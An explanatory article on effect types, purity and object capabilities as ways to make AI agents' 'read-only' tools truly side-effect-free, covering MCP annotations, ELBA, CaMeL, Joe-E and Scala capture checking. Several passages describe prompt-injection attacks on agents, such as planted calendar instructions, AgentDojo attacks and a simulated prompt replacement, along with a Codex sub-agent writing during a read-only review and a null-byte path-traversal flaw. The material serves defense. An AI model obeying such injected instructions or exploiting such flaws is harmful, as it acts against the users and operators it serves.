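# Effect systems, purity and read-only capabilities as guarantees that an agent's tools have no side effects

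## What it means for a tool to be read-only

Effect systems, purity and read-only capabilities are techniques for limiting what code can change, or for proving in advance that it changes nothing. They come from research on programming languages and computer security, most of it older than today's language models. They matter for AI agents because agents act by calling tools, and many of those tools are labeled "read-only" even though nothing prevents them from making changes.

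An AI agent is a program that runs a language model in a loop. The model receives a task and a list of tools, which are functions it can request by name, such as searching the web, opening a file or querying a database. When the model writes out such a request (a tool call), the surrounding software runs the function and adds the result to the model's input, and the model continues. The model itself only produces text, so the agent can affect the world only through tool calls.

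A side effect is any change a call makes to state outside itself, such as a file, a database row, a log or another machine. Returning a result doesn't count. A read-only tool may read outside state but is not supposed to change it.

Developers care about the read-only label because it lets software skip checks. Many agent products ask for the user's approval before a call that could do damage, but run read-only calls without asking. If a connection drops during a call, the software can't tell whether the call took effect, but it can resend the call if the tool is read-only. An agent can also run read-only tools while it drafts a plan or a preview, before the user has agreed to anything. Because nobody is watching these calls, a tool wrongly labeled read-only can do harm unnoticed.

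An agent might have a tool, `find_invoice(id)`, that takes an invoice number, reads the matching record from a billing service and returns it. A call also adds a line to a log and saves the answer in a cache, a local copy that lets the next identical call avoid using the network. The request to the billing service runs other people's code, which may keep its own log, count the request against a monthly quota, or mark the invoice as viewed. Most programmers would still mark the tool read-only. Whether these effects matter depends on the observer, meaning whoever might notice them. An operator who reads the logs sees a new line for every call, even though the user who wanted the invoice sees none of these effects.

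A developer can declare that a tool is read-only or enforce it. A declaration states, in the tool's name, documentation or metadata, that the tool changes nothing. A false declaration looks the same as a true one until something breaks. Enforcement prevents the change, for example with a compiler that rejects the code, an operating system that blocks writes to the file, or a database account without write permission. Much of the work on enforcement falls into two families, effect types and capabilities. Effect types let a compiler work out from the code what a function could change, while capabilities let code use only the things that someone has given it.

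### The label in the Model Context Protocol

Much agent software takes its declarations from the Model Context Protocol (MCP), which the programmer Simon Willison (2026) describes in *Stateless MCP has recaptured my interest* as a standard way to expose tools to agents. Anthropic introduced it in November 2024. By July 2026 developers were downloading its main software kits nearly half a billion times a month, according to the Model Context Protocol (2026) release announcement. An MCP server offers tools, and an MCP client inside the agent product fetches the list and sends the calls. The server's author can attach annotations to each tool, including four true-or-false hints about what the tool does. The definitions and defaults below come from the Model Context Protocol schema, and the last column gives the maintainers' examples of what a client might do with each hint.

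| Hint | Meaning when true | Value if the author omits it | What a client might do when it is true |
|---|---|---|---|
| `readOnlyHint` | The tool does not modify its environment | false | Skip the confirmation dialog |
| `destructiveHint` | The tool may make destructive updates, where false means additive updates only | true | Show a warning first |
| `idempotentHint` | Repeating the call with the same arguments has no additional effect | false | Retry after a failure |
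| `openWorldHint` | The tool may interact with an open-ended world of external entities | true | Check the output for untrusted content |

The hints about destruction and repetition have meaning only for a tool whose `readOnlyHint` is false.

By default, a tool without annotations is assumed to change things, possibly destroy them, be unsafe to repeat and reach the outside world. These pessimistic defaults are sensible because an author who forgets the annotations only causes an unnecessary dialog for the user, and harm comes only from an author who writes "true" where it's false. In practice, the protection is less consistent because many servers ship without annotations and clients differ in how strictly they apply the defaults, as the Model Context Protocol maintainers acknowledged in a March 2026 blog post.

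Under a strict reading of the hints, `readOnlyHint` is false for `find_invoice`, because writing to the cache and the log modifies the environment. The cache keeps only the last answer, so each new answer overwrites an old one, which is hardly an additive update. The tool isn't idempotent either, because every repeated call adds a log line. Whether the billing service counts as external depends on where the server runs. The tool therefore gets the worst value on three of the four hints, and arguably on all of them, which puts it in the same class as a tool that wipes disks. No sensible author would label a harmless lookup that way. The author instead sets `readOnlyHint` to true, meaning something like "changes nothing you would care about". The schema doesn't settle whether that is correct, because it leaves "environment" undefined.

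Under the schema, the hints come with no guarantee of accuracy, and clients should never base decisions about tool use on annotations from untrusted servers. Justin Spahr-Summers, one of the protocol's creators, objected while reviewing the original proposal, asking what a client can do with a flag that it can't trust. Basil Hosmer, another participant in that discussion, argued that clients should ignore annotations from untrusted servers entirely. The published rule is a compromise. Every annotation is a hint that clients must distrust by default, but each client decides how much weight to give it based on the information it has about the server.

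The maintainers defend the hints as giving clients a basic vocabulary for risk. A company that runs its own servers behind a login already has reason to trust them, so it can base policy on their hints. A rule engine can combine the hints with other signals, for example to block tools that reach the open internet once a session has read private data. GitHub's MCP server has a read-only mode, which about 17% of users have switched on. All of these uses rely on a source of trust other than the hint itself.

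In the same post, the maintainers propose a test for new annotations. If an annotation's usefulness depends on its being true, they argue, it is really a contract and belongs in the authorization layer, the transport or the runtime. By that test, the existing `readOnlyHint` looks much like a contract, because skipping a confirmation makes sense only if the hint is true. The maintainers nearly concede this. They call the hint useless for that decision when it comes from an untrusted server, and they refer anyone who needs a guarantee to network controls or sandboxing, which limits what running code can reach. They also report that most clients treat any installed server as trusted and make no finer distinction.

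The annotations have changed little since. The current specification dates from 28 July 2026, and the Model Context Protocol (2026) changelog for it lists no change to them. An interest group for tool annotations formed in the spring. Model Context Protocol's *Tool Annotations Charter*, dated 20 April 2026, puts four draft proposals on the group's agenda, including labels for sensitive data and a check that runs before a call. It leaves open whether annotations should be allowed to vary from one call to the next. Review of these drafts may take a while, because tool annotations are not among the five priority areas for scarce review time in the Model Context Protocol roadmap of August 2026. The next version of the specification is due on 30 March 2027, according to the Model Context Protocol (2026) blog.

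Two other changes in the July version do make it more important to know which calls are safe to repeat. Earlier versions let a client resume a response stream after a break. Now a broken stream loses the request, and the client must issue it again as a new request with a new identifier. If the server had already finished the work, it does the work twice, and it can't readily spot the repeat because the identifier is new. The other change is that a tool that needs the user's confirmation partway through now returns its question to the client, which retries the original call with the answer attached, so anything the tool did before asking may happen again. Repeating a call to `find_invoice` only adds a log line, but repeating a call to a tool that issues refunds could issue a second refund.

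### A read-only review that saved a file

Labelling a task read-only does not by itself prevent side effects. In 2026, a user of Codex, OpenAI's coding agent, reported that a sub-agent (a second agent that takes on part of a larger job) had been assigned a read-only review of code changes waiting to go into a project's history. During the review, the sub-agent called an image-generation tool, which saved an unrelated picture outside the project's repository. The files in the repository did not change. *ETAS* (Tan, Wang and colleagues, 2026), which proposes a programming language whose compiler tracks what agents may do, cites the case to argue that an unchanged repository does not prove a review was read-only.

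The only evidence is one bug report from one user. Its title suggests either prompt injection (instructions that an attacker hides in text the model reads) or a corrupted tool call, and a contributor to the project classified the incident as model behaviour. The known damage was a stray picture. Still, one case is enough to support Tan and colleagues' point. The sub-agent's assignment was described as read-only, but it still had access to a tool that writes files, and no mechanism stopped the write. A check for changes in the repository would have found none and missed the write.

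### Change, dependence and undoing

People often use "read-only", "pure" and "safe" interchangeably, and so confuse three questions about a tool call: whether it changes anything, whether its result depends only on its arguments, and whether anyone can undo it.

A function is pure if it changes nothing that the chosen observer can see and its result depends only on its arguments. Two toy examples in the MCP schema illustrate the difference between these conditions. `calculate_sum` adds two numbers, so it is pure. `get_current_time` also changes nothing, but it gives a different answer every time, so it is read-only without being pure. If its author removed the cache and the log, `find_invoice` would be read-only but still not pure, because a customer can pay an invoice between two calls, and the same invoice number will then return a different record. An agent may repeat a read-only call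 freely, but it may keep an old answer forever only if the call is pure. For example, an agent that relies on yesterday's "unpaid" may send a reminder to someone who paid this morning.

A tool can do harm even if its result depends only on its arguments. For example, it could delete a file and always return "done".

Whether a tool's changes can be undone is a separate question from whether the tool is read-only. Moving a file to the trash changes the disk, even though the user can move it back. Sending an email is irrevocable. A user might reasonably let an agent make reversible changes without asking, but a tool that makes them is still not read-only. Reversal also works only if someone kept the old state and nobody acted on the new one in the meantime.

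MCP's hints cover only whether a tool changes anything. `idempotentHint` describes the effects of repeating a call, not whether the answer stays the same. `destructiveHint` comes closest to indicating whether a change can be undone, but some non-destructive changes are permanent and some destructive ones are reversible. Sending an email only adds a message to somebody's inbox but can't be undone, while a destructive overwrite may be easy to reverse from a backup.

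### Who is at fault when the label is wrong

A label can be false or useless because its author was careless, a model was misled or a server is malicious, and a mechanism that addresses one of these causes may not address another.

Suppose a developer correctly marks `find_invoice` as read-only, and a year later a colleague adds a line that flags each invoice as viewed but doesn't update the annotation. The annotation is now wrong, though nobody lied. MCP's trust rule doesn't help, because the company has good reason to trust its own server. Effect types can catch this kind of mistake by checking the code automatically on every build. The check works best when developers aren't trying to get around it.

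A misled model can make the wrong call even when every label is accurate. Language models follow instructions they find in text, and they can't reliably tell the user's instructions from an attacker's. The MCP maintainers cite a demonstration in which researchers planted instructions in the description of a calendar event. The agent had one tool that could read the event and another that could run code on the user's machine. Looking up a calendar event changes nothing, so the call that brought in the planted instructions would have been allowed under an accurate read-only label. Better labels do not help with this, but developers can protect against it by giving the model no tools that write from the start, or by running those tools under limits that the model cannot lift. The Codex incident is also a case of a misled model, if the contributor's classification is right.

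A malicious server is the hardest of these to handle. Its owner can set `readOnlyHint` to true on a tool that deletes files, and the client can't type-check code it never sees. The operating system can still confine a server that runs on the user's own machine, but if the server runs elsewhere, the user controls only what the agent sends and which credentials it uses. For `find_invoice`, the user could give the agent a billing service account that isn't allowed to alter invoices, though this protects them only as far as the billing service enforces the restriction.

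## Effect types: proving from the code that a function only computes

A compiler that has a tool's source code can check the read-only label instead of trusting the author. To do this, it must work out what each function in the tool may do and how those effects combine when functions call each other. An effect type is the part of a function's type that lists the effects a call may have. For example, the ordinary type of `find_invoice` records that it takes an invoice number and returns an invoice. Its effect type adds that a call may use the network, change the cache and write to the log.

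The idea dates from the 1980s. Gifford and Lucassen (1986), in *Integrating Functional and Imperative Programming*, started with a small fixed set of effects, and Lucassen (1987), in *Types and Effects*, described effects in much finer detail. Their main interest was speed and clean language design, not security. A compiler can safely run two parts of a program in parallel if it can establish that neither part writes to memory the other uses. An agent product needs much the same information to determine whether it can repeat a call.

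Compilers of the time already estimated effects by tracing which functions call which. This works badly when a program can pass functions as values, because the compiler often can't determine which function a call will run. Agent software makes many such calls, since it typically looks up a tool by name in a table and runs the function it finds there. Lucassen stored a function's effects in its type, so that the compiler has this information wherever the program passes the function.

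The compiler works out a type T and a set of effects E for every expression e in the program. T describes the value that e produces, and E contains the effects that producing it may have. In Lucassen's language, each effect pairs an action (allocate, read or write) with a region, which is a group of memory locations that the programmer has named. If e has no effects, E is empty.

Defining a function has no effects, however much damage the function could do later. Its type therefore stores the effects of its body as latent effects, which count only when something calls it. To run a call e1(e2), the computer evaluates e1 to get the function, evaluates e2 to get the argument, and then runs the function's body. The effects of the call are the union of all three:

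```
effects of e1(e2)  =  effects of evaluating e1
                   ∪  effects of evaluating e2
                   ∪  latent effects of the function
```

### Checking find_invoice

Suppose the code of `find_invoice` looks like this, with a helper, `format_invoice`, that only arranges the record's fields into readable text:

```
find_invoice(id):
    if not in_cache(id):
        save(fetch(id))
    write_log(id)
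    return format_invoice(cached())
```

The compiler starts from the primitives, the basic operations whose effects somebody has declared by hand. Here `fetch` has the effect "network", `save` has "write cache", `in_cache` and `cached` have "read cache", and `write_log` has "write log". The call rule then gives:

| Expression | Evaluating the function | Evaluating the argument | Running the body | Union |
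|---|---|---|---|---|
| `fetch(id)` | none | none | network | network |
| `save(fetch(id))` | none | network | write cache | network, write cache |
| `format_invoice(cached())` | none | read cache | none | read cache |

The union over all lines is network, read cache, write cache and write log. This set is an upper bound. `find_invoice` doesn't use the network when the answer is already in the cache, but the compiler can't determine in advance which branch of the `if` will run, so it includes the effects of both. Lucassen called the rule for conditionals "rather conservative" for the same reason. The rule errs on the safe side, because the compiler may list an effect that never happens but shouldn't omit one that does.

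The helper `format_invoice` has an empty effect set, even though the program calls it on data from the cache, because the read happens before the helper starts. Reads count as effects too, so a function with an empty set is pure, and one whose set contains only reads is read-only. `find_invoice` is neither, but the compiler can now list exactly which writes keep it from being read-only. That list is more useful than a single true-or-false hint about an undefined "environment", because the developer can decide to permit those writes and no others.

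After the developer declares the permitted effects, a colleague might change `find_invoice` so that it also flags invoices as viewed. The build then fails if the new operation has its own effect, such as "write billing". But the function probably sets the flag by sending the billing service another network request. If requests that read and requests that modify both carry the label "network", the function's set of effects doesn't change and the build succeeds. To catch this mistake, the developer needs separate primitives and labels for the two kinds of request.

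### Functions that take other functions

The effects of many functions depend on the functions passed to them. The standard example is `map`, which applies a function to every element of a list and returns the list of results. Applying `format_invoice` to a hundred records has no effects, while applying `find_invoice` to a hundred invoice numbers may write a hundred log lines. A compiler that had to give `map` one fixed set of effects would have to include every possible effect, so every program that used `map` would look dangerous.

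Effect polymorphism solves this with a variable that stands for a set of effects:

```
map : (list of A, function from A to B with effects µ) -> list of B, with effects µ
```

A call to `map` has the same effect µ as the function passed to it. Lucassen introduced such variables for effects and regions, and illustrated them with `map` under its Lisp name, `mapcar`.

Effect systems also need a rule that lets a function be used where its caller allows more effects than the function has. Suppose a setting chooses between the real `find_invoice` and a demo version that returns a made-up invoice and has no effects. The two functions have different effect types, so a compiler that required the types to match exactly would reject the program. Under the more permissive rule, called subeffecting, the compiler accepts both functions wherever the real one's effects are allowed. Talpin and Jouvelot (1992),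 in *Polymorphic type, region and effect inference*, added subeffecting partly to accept programs like this, which an earlier system had rejected. The rule lets a pure function be used where a read-only function is expected, but not a function that writes.

### Haskell's IO and Koka's effect rows

Haskell, the best-known language that separates pure code from the rest, does it with a type named `IO`. There `format_invoice` would have the type `Invoice -> String`, and a `find_invoice` that returns text would have the type `InvoiceId -> IO String`. Any function that runs an `IO` computation as part of its work must have `IO` in its own type, and so must its callers, all the way up. (Haskell has escape hatches from this rule, of which `unsafePerformIO` is the most notorious.)

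`IO` is a coarse label. Reading the clock and wiping the disk both have `IO` in their types, so the compiler can distinguish computing from acting but not reading from writing. The method itself allows finer labels. Haskell's `IO` is a monad, a general construction for sequencing computations, and *The Marriage of Effects and Monads* (1999) shows that Talpin and Jouvelot's whole system, including regions, carries over to monads. Haskell programmers can also define narrower types.

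Koka, a research language from Microsoft, lists a function's effects individually, as a row of labels in its type (Leijen 2014, *Koka*). A function that squares a number gets the label `total`, which means it has no effects. If the programmer adds a line that prints the number, the compiler automatically changes the label to `io`. Other labels cover exceptions, possible non-termination, random results, and allocating, reading or writing memory. A row can also end in a variable, as in the type of `map`.

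Leijen calls a function "pure" if it may throw an exception or run forever but has no other effects, which is a looser definition than most people would expect. Leijen points out that purity means the same thing in Haskell, where a function from `Int` to `Int` changes nothing but may still crash or never return.

Koka can also leave an effect out of a function's type when code outside the function can't observe it. Leijen's example computes Fibonacci numbers by repeatedly updating two variables. The variables are created inside the function and disappear when it returns, so the compiler removes the memory effects and gives the function the type `total`. It can't do this for the cache in `find_invoice`, because the cache has to survive until the next call. Koka's built-in labels put all input and output under `io`, so a developer who wants to distinguish writing a log line from issuing a refund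 has to define more specific labels, which the design allows.

### What the proof promises

Designers of effect systems usually prove a soundness theorem, which connects the compiler's effect sets to what programs do when they run. Talpin and Jouvelot's version compares an expression's effect set with a trace, a record of every memory location the running program created, read or wrote. If the expression passes the checker and finishes running, its effect set covers every entry in the trace. Lucassen's proposition establishes the same guarantee for each step of a run, so it also applies to programs that never finish.

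The theorem holds only if the primitives are labelled correctly. Lucassen's proof requires the three operations that touch memory to each carry the matching effect, and anyone can check three operations by hand. A real tool depends on network libraries, database drivers and operating system calls, often written in another language, and the compiler accepts each of their declared labels without checking it. If someone labels `fetch` as having no effects, the compiler will wrongly certify that `find_invoice` doesn't use the network.

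Proofs can be wrong too. In an updated report on *Koka*, Leijen (2013) notes that the previous version contained a wrong lemma, which led to mistakes in several proofs. Leijen corrected them, and they aren't a reason to dismiss the method, but a proof on paper is weaker evidence than one a computer has checked.

### Making the agent write typed programs

*Language-Based Agent Control* (Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova, 2026) applies effect types to agents. In its Haskell system, ELBA, the model writes a program instead of requesting tools one at a time, and the compiler must accept the program before any of it runs. The developer supplies a prompt, a list of functions the program may use, and the type the program must have. If the program has the wrong type, ELBA sends the compiler's error message back to the model, which tries again.

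Their simplest example is a calculator on a public website, where the required type is `Int`, a whole number. A malicious visitor asks it to delete all files on the server and then compute the factorial of 5. The model may well write a program that runs the delete command, but the compiler will reject it, so the defense doesn't depend on the model refusing the request. The function that runs system commands has `IO` in its type, so the whole program does too, and it therefore isn't an `Int`.

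`Int` rules out slightly less than Zhou and colleagues suggest. They say it forbids exceptions, but on Leijen's account a Haskell `Int` can still fail or run forever, so a visitor could tie up the server with an endless calculation. The type also does not record the query to the language model, which is a network request and can return a different answer each time. The soundness proof for ELBA counts only tool calls as observable effects.

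Zhou and colleagues' main example is an agent that compiles bibliographies and may write only entries that come from DBLP, a database of computer science publications. The developer defines a new effect type, `BibIO`, with three operations: search DBLP, fetch an entry, and append an entry to the bibliography file. The agent's program may combine these with any amount of effect-free code, such as sorting and filtering. It can't call Haskell's general function for writing files, because that function has type `IO`, not `BibIO`. The append operation accepts only values of type `Trusted Bib`, which only the fetch operation can produce, so the agent can't append an invented entry. A developer could make a read-only version by leaving out the append operation.

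The agent's program can start a sub-agent, for instance to look at the first search result and decide what to do next. A sub-agent started inside a `BibIO` program must also produce a `BibIO` program. The parent can give it a stricter type, such as one with no effects, but not a looser one. The Codex sub-agent that saved a stray picture during a read-only review had no such limit. If its task had required a type without file writes, the image tool would have failed the check.

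Zhou and colleagues prove that any property Haskell's types guarantee for ordinary programs also holds for programs that contain agent calls. The proof treats the model as an arbitrary function that might return any program, so the result holds even for a gullible or hostile model, provided that the three `BibIO` operations behave as their types specify.

Zhou and colleagues tested the bibliography agent on 100 tasks with Anthropic's Sonnet 5. It produced 925 citations, none with a wrong author, year or identifier. A conventional agent with a web search tool produced 1,002 citations, 19 of them wrong, and used about four times as many model calls. The comparison isn't entirely fair to the conventional agent, because it worked from web results and memory instead of DBLP. A single tool that fetches an entry and appends it in one step would also have prevented invented entries, as Zhou and colleagues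 say, but types still let the agent write code to sort and select the entries.

### The comparison with CaMeL

The larger experiment uses AgentDojo, a benchmark that gives agents ordinary office tasks and plants malicious instructions in the data they read. It measures how many tasks the agent completes and how many attacks it resists. Zhou and colleagues used the part set in the chat service Slack, which pairs each of 21 user tasks with each of 5 attacks, for 105 pairs in total. They compared ELBA with CaMeL, an earlier defense in which the model writes its whole program before reading any data, so malicious text can't influence which tools the program calls. A second model, without tools, processes the untrusted text. CaMeL can also track where each piece of data came from and block calls that break a policy.

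Both systems can run with or without such policies. This is how many of the 105 tasks each completed under AgentDojo's "direct" style of attack:

| Model | ELBA, policies on | CaMeL, policies on | ELBA, policies off | CaMeL, policies off |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Opus 4.7 | 52 | 24 | 88 | 69 |
| Opus 4.8 | 49 | 30 | 93 | 78 |
| GPT 5.4 | 51 | 23 | 84 | 82 |
| Sonnet 5 | 43 | 25 | 78 | 56 |

With policies on, ELBA completed 195 of 420 tasks across the four models, while CaMeL completed 102. Zhou and colleagues attribute the gap to ELBA's freedom to read data before deciding what to do next. Working this way also made ELBA take about three times as long as CaMeL.

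These runs provide no evidence about security, because every model resisted every attack under both systems, even with policies off. Zhou and colleagues therefore simulated a much worse attack. Whenever a sub-agent read text that contained the attack, they replaced the sub-agent's entire prompt with the attacker's text, so that it carried out the attacker's orders. They ran the 105 pairs seven times per model. With policies off, between 16% and 42% of the attacks succeeded, depending on the model. With policies on, none of the 2,940 attacks succeeded, but the models completed only 40% to 48% of the tasks, compared with 67% to 76% with policies off.

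Effect types were only partly responsible for the result. The policies came from LIO, a Haskell library that labels data with its source and checks the labels while the program runs. If a program has read an untrusted web page and then tries to post a message, LIO stops it. The compiler ensured that the agent's program used LIO's operations and couldn't bypass them. The experiment is therefore good evidence for combining types with run-time checks, but it doesn't measure what types achieve alone.

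### Labels that a model only reads

A much cheaper approach is to label each tool with its effects and hope that the model behaves accordingly. Kovalenko and Redchych (2026), in *Small Agents Should Know What Their Tools Do*, tested how far training gets a model toward this. Their test environment, EffectWorld, gives every tool one of four labels:

| Label | Meaning | Rule for the agent |
|---|---|---|
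| Pure | Computes from its arguments | Don't call it for a value you already have |
| Read | Looks at state, changes nothing | Don't repeat it unless something has changed |
| Write | Makes a change that someone can correct later | Read the state first |
| Destructive | Can't be taken back | Ask the user first |

"Destructive" here includes sending an email or paying for an order, so the label fits the need for confirmation better than MCP's hint of the same name. The tools' authors still declare the labels themselves, and no compiler derives them from the code. The label "pure" looks doubtful for the tool that returns the current date, because its answer changes every day.

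A program replays each run against the labels and counts violations, such as a destructive call that the user hadn't confirmed. Kovalenko and Redchych trained small open models on about 6,000 well-behaved example runs in an office setting, mixed with about 15,000 public examples of tool use. They tested the models on new office tasks and on an online shop whose tools weren't in the training data. The models received the rules in words but, in most versions, not the labels.

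The training worked very well on familiar tools. Before training, Qwen3-4B, a model with four billion parameters, completed 53% of the office tasks and made 94 unconfirmed destructive calls in 498 tasks. After training on the unfiltered mix of examples, it completed 99% with no violations. In the shop, the main version of the training raised its completion rate from 74% to 83%, but also raised its number of unconfirmed destructive calls from 7 in 547 tasks to 24. The other three models changed in the same direction.

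The model seems to have learned to ask before using certain tools, not before using destructive tools in general. Kovalenko and Redchych tried to fix this by writing the labels into the tool descriptions and giving the office tools varied names during training. Unconfirmed destructive calls in the shop fell from 24 to 19, which could be chance. The models are small and most were trained from a single random seed, and a frontier model would probably do better. Still, of these versions, the untrained model was the most careful in the shop, so training on labeled tools doesn't guarantee caution with new ones. In ELBA, by contrast, a program that uses a forbidden operation doesn't run, regardless of what the model has learned.

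### The burden on programmers and models

Effect types have existed for 40 years, and hardly anyone outside research uses them. In *Lightweight Polymorphic Effects*, Rytz, Odersky and Haller could name only one effect system adopted by a widely used industrial language, Java's checked exceptions, which make a function declare the errors it may throw. They blame verbosity, especially in functions like `map`, whose effects depend on their arguments. Lucassen had anticipated this problem and conceded that adding regions had made the burden of declarations worse.

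The standard reply is inference, where the compiler works out the effects and the programmer writes few or none of them. Talpin and Jouvelot gave an algorithm for this and proved it correct. Tate and Leijen (2010) designed a system with inference and a few broad effects, so that programmers could read the types easily. An earlier version of Koka used subeffecting, but Leijen found that the inferred types often filled up with complicated constraints, and using rows instead made the types simpler. By 2014 Koka's own developers had written sample programs in it, including a Markdown processor and a chat application, which is encouraging but a long way from industrial use.

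Even with inference, someone has to declare a tool's permitted effects at the point where the agent calls it. Otherwise, if a colleague adds a write to `find_invoice`, the compiler just infers a larger set of effects and reports no error. This takes one line per tool, which seems reasonable and is about as much effort as filling in MCP's hints.

Strong models seem to lose little time to compiler errors in ELBA. Across 2,688 AgentDojo runs, the model had to rewrite a rejected program about once in every eight runs, and the retries took 3.4% of the total time. Seven runs failed because the model never produced an acceptable program. Programs also had to pass the type checker in the versions of ELBA with policies off, and those versions completed more tasks under direct attack than CaMeL did with its policies off. The large loss of usefulness came from the policies, which also blocked some legitimate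 work. It is unclear how smaller models would cope with Haskell's type errors, because Zhou and colleagues tested only large commercial ones.

Effect types also work only on code in a language that has them, and this limitation is harder to avoid. AgentDojo's tools are written in Python, so ELBA had to call them in a separate process. The Haskell compiler checked how the agent's program used the tools, but not whether the tools' own code matched their types.

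## Capabilities: code that cannot act because it holds no authority

Effect types record what a function may do, while capabilities limit what it can reach. A tool without access to the billing system can't alter an invoice, however badly written the tool is. A capability in this sense is an unforgeable reference that both names a resource and gives the right to use it. (The term doesn't refer here to an AI system's abilities.) A file object in a running program is a typical example, since only code that holds the object can use the file.

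Object-capability languages extend this to everything outside a function's own calculations. Files, network connections and stored data are objects, and code can affect an object only through a reference to it. Code gets a reference by creating the object, by receiving the reference from other code, or by having it in the environment it starts with. A reviewer can find out what a piece of code could change by following the references it holds, then the references stored inside those objects, and so on until none are left, since the code can't affect anything outside that set.

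Under this rule, `find_invoice` can't simply call `fetch` or `write_log`. Someone has to hand it the objects that do the work:

```
find_invoice(billing, cache, log, id)
```

Suppose `billing` offers only one operation, fetching a record. A colleague who later wants to flag each invoice as viewed has no operation to call and must ask for more access. An effect type with one broad "network" label would have missed this change. But the protection depends on how narrow the references are. If `billing` is a general network client, the colleague can send any request, and the rule doesn't help.

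Access to the log can be limited too. *Joe-E* (Mettler, Wagner and Close, 2010) describes a log object with a private text buffer and a single method, which adds an entry. Code that holds this object can add entries but can't change or delete old ones, and a reviewer can confirm that by reading one short class.

### What a language has to give up

Most popular languages break the object-capability rule in several places. Any Java code can build a file object from a file's name, then read, overwrite or delete that file if the user's account has permission. This is ambient authority, meaning power that code has without being given it, so withholding references does little to restrict such code.

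Joe-E is a subset of Java without these loopholes. Every Joe-E program is also an ordinary Java program, but a checker called the verifier rejects code that uses forbidden features. These are the main ones:

| Java feature | How it breaks the rule | Joe-E's restriction |
|---|---|---|
| Opening a file by name | Any code can turn a piece of text into access to a file | Code must receive a file or directory object |
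| Mutable global variables | Code can change shared state, or pick up a reference that other code left there | Global variables must be constant, and so must everything they point to |
| Native methods, written in another language | They can forge references or do anything else | Joe-E code can't define them |
| Reflection, which inspects a program's parts while it runs | Code can get at another object's private fields | Joe-E code gets only a safe version |
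| Exceptions that carry objects | An error can deliver a capability to a caller that shouldn't have it | Exceptions must be immutable |

The rule about files is hard to apply because someone has to go through Java's standard library and decide which methods are safe. A Java file object has a method that returns the directory containing the file. By calling it repeatedly, code that holds one file can reach the root directory and, from there, every file on the disk. Java also has a constructor that takes a directory and the name of a file inside it, but if the directory is null, the name can be a path to anywhere on the disk. Joe-E excludes both and supplies a safe replacement for the constructor.

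Mettler and colleagues call this manual sorting a substantial weakness of their approach. An earlier review of E, the language that most influenced Joe-E, found that its designers had accidentally allowed several unsafe library methods. Joe-E's library also had a flaw in how it checked file names for "..", which means the parent directory. Java allows a name to contain a null byte, which marks the end of a string in C. The underlying C code stopped reading at that byte, so a name could pass the check and still lead out of the permitted directory. Joe-E's maintainers fixed this in version 2.2.3 of the library.

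Most existing Java programs would fail the verifier, and programmers usually have to restructure them to make them pass, so that each part receives the capabilities it needs. Mettler and colleagues didn't find the restrictions a serious problem in their own programs, but they expect other programmers to need training.

### Reading purity off a method's signature

Pure methods are easy to recognize in a language without ambient authority. Finifter, Mettler and colleagues (2008) did this with Joe-E in *Verifiable functional purity in java*. Until then, nobody could automatically prove methods pure in a widely used language like Java. Their test uses only a method's signature, the line that declares its name and parameter types. A method is pure if all its parameters have immutable types, including the receiver (the object the method belongs to).

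Such a method can reach only its parameters, its receiver, the global constants, and any objects it creates. Everything that existed before the call is immutable, so the method can change only its new objects, which no other code can observe during the call. It therefore has no side effects. Nothing it reads can vary between calls, so the same arguments must also give the same result, unless the language has some hidden source of variation.

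Joe-E must also block those hidden sources of nondeterminism. A method can't read the clock or use a random number generator unless it is given access to one. Joe-E also bans catching serious errors, because a method that could catch an out-of-memory error might return a different answer on a smaller machine. The Berkeley dissertation *Language and Framework Support for Reviewably-Secure Software Systems* calls this property determinism by default.

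By this test, `format_invoice` is pure if `Invoice` is an immutable type. The programmer declares it immutable, and the verifier checks that the program can never reassign the type's fields and that each field holds either a basic value, such as a number, or another immutable object. The parameters of `find_invoice` show that it fails the test, because they include a cache and a log.

Some pure methods fail the test. A method that takes a mutable list and returns a sorted copy has no side effects, but its signature would also allow it to sort the original. The test can also expose problems that a programmer might overlook. Mettler and colleagues describe a plug-in for decoding images, whose one method takes an array of bytes and returns a bitmap. They want to ensure that a malicious plug-in can do nothing worse than decode an image wrongly. But Java's arrays are always mutable, so the plug-in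 could overwrite the caller's copy of the image data. The method would pass the purity test only if it took one of Joe-E's immutable arrays.

Finifter and colleagues tried the technique on an encryption library, an experimental voting machine and an HTML parser that originally had more than 10,000 lines of Java. They restructured each program until its top-level methods passed the test. Purity makes run-time checks in programs like these much more informative. For example, a program can encrypt a file and immediately decrypt it to check that the result matches the original. A match normally shows only that decryption worked once, but if decryption is pure, it will give the same result for the same data and key next year. However, these programs mostly transform data they already have, so they are easier cases than a tool whose main job is to fetch something.

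A related test recognizes methods that are read-only but not necessarily pure. It requires read-only parameters instead of immutable ones. A method can't change an object through a read-only reference, but other code may still change that object. *Pure methods for roDOT (an extended version)* (Dort, Li and colleagues, 2024) proves the test correct for roDOT, a small mathematical model of Scala, a language related to Java. It shows that a method that passes the test never modifies an object that existed before the call, and that swapping two calls to such methods doesn't affect the program's result. Dort and colleagues checked all their proofs with Coq, a program for verifying proofs. But roDOT covers only objects in memory, not files or networks.

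Waterken, a web server written mostly in Joe-E, enforces read-only behaviour at run time. A GET request is supposed to read something without changing it, though many sites don't follow this rule. Waterken handles each GET request as a transaction and aborts it if the application has modified anything. It can detect every modification because the application can't open a file by name or change a global variable, so all its changes are in objects that the server can inspect. The server has about 13,000 lines of Joe-E and 4,000 lines of unrestricted Java, and reviewers have to examine the Java more carefully.

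This is close to an enforced version of MCP's `readOnlyHint`. It is also strict enough that if `find_invoice` kept its cache among the application's own objects, Waterken would abort the first request that saved an answer there.

### Capabilities that show up in types

Object capabilities are hard to track with ordinary function types, because a programmer can pass on a function that contains a reference its type doesn't reveal. For example, a function that takes an invoice and returns text may only format the invoice, or it may also email the invoice to somebody if its author had access to a mail connection.

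In *Stoic*, Liu, Stucki and colleagues proposed a separate type for functions that hold no capabilities of their own. A "stoic" function may use capabilities that its caller passes as arguments, but it can't capture any from the surrounding code. It also can't capture an ordinary function, since that function might hold a capability. They wrote the types of stoic functions with `->` and those of all other functions with `=>`. They also proved, for a small model language, that stoic functions don't interfere with memory that their callers didn't pass in.

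Scala 3 has adopted these arrows as part of a more detailed system called capture checking, which Scala's *Tracked Capabilities Overview* explains. A type can include a capture set, which lists the capabilities that a value may hold. If the three objects in the invoice example are already in place, so that a caller has to supply only the invoice number, the type of `find_invoice` might be:

```
InvoiceId ->{billing, cache, log} Invoice
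```

The type `InvoiceId -> Invoice` has an empty capture set, so a function of this type holds no capabilities, whereas a function of type `InvoiceId => Invoice` may hold any capability. The compiler accepts a function with a smaller capture set wherever the program allows a larger one, much as subeffecting lets a function with fewer effects replace one with more.

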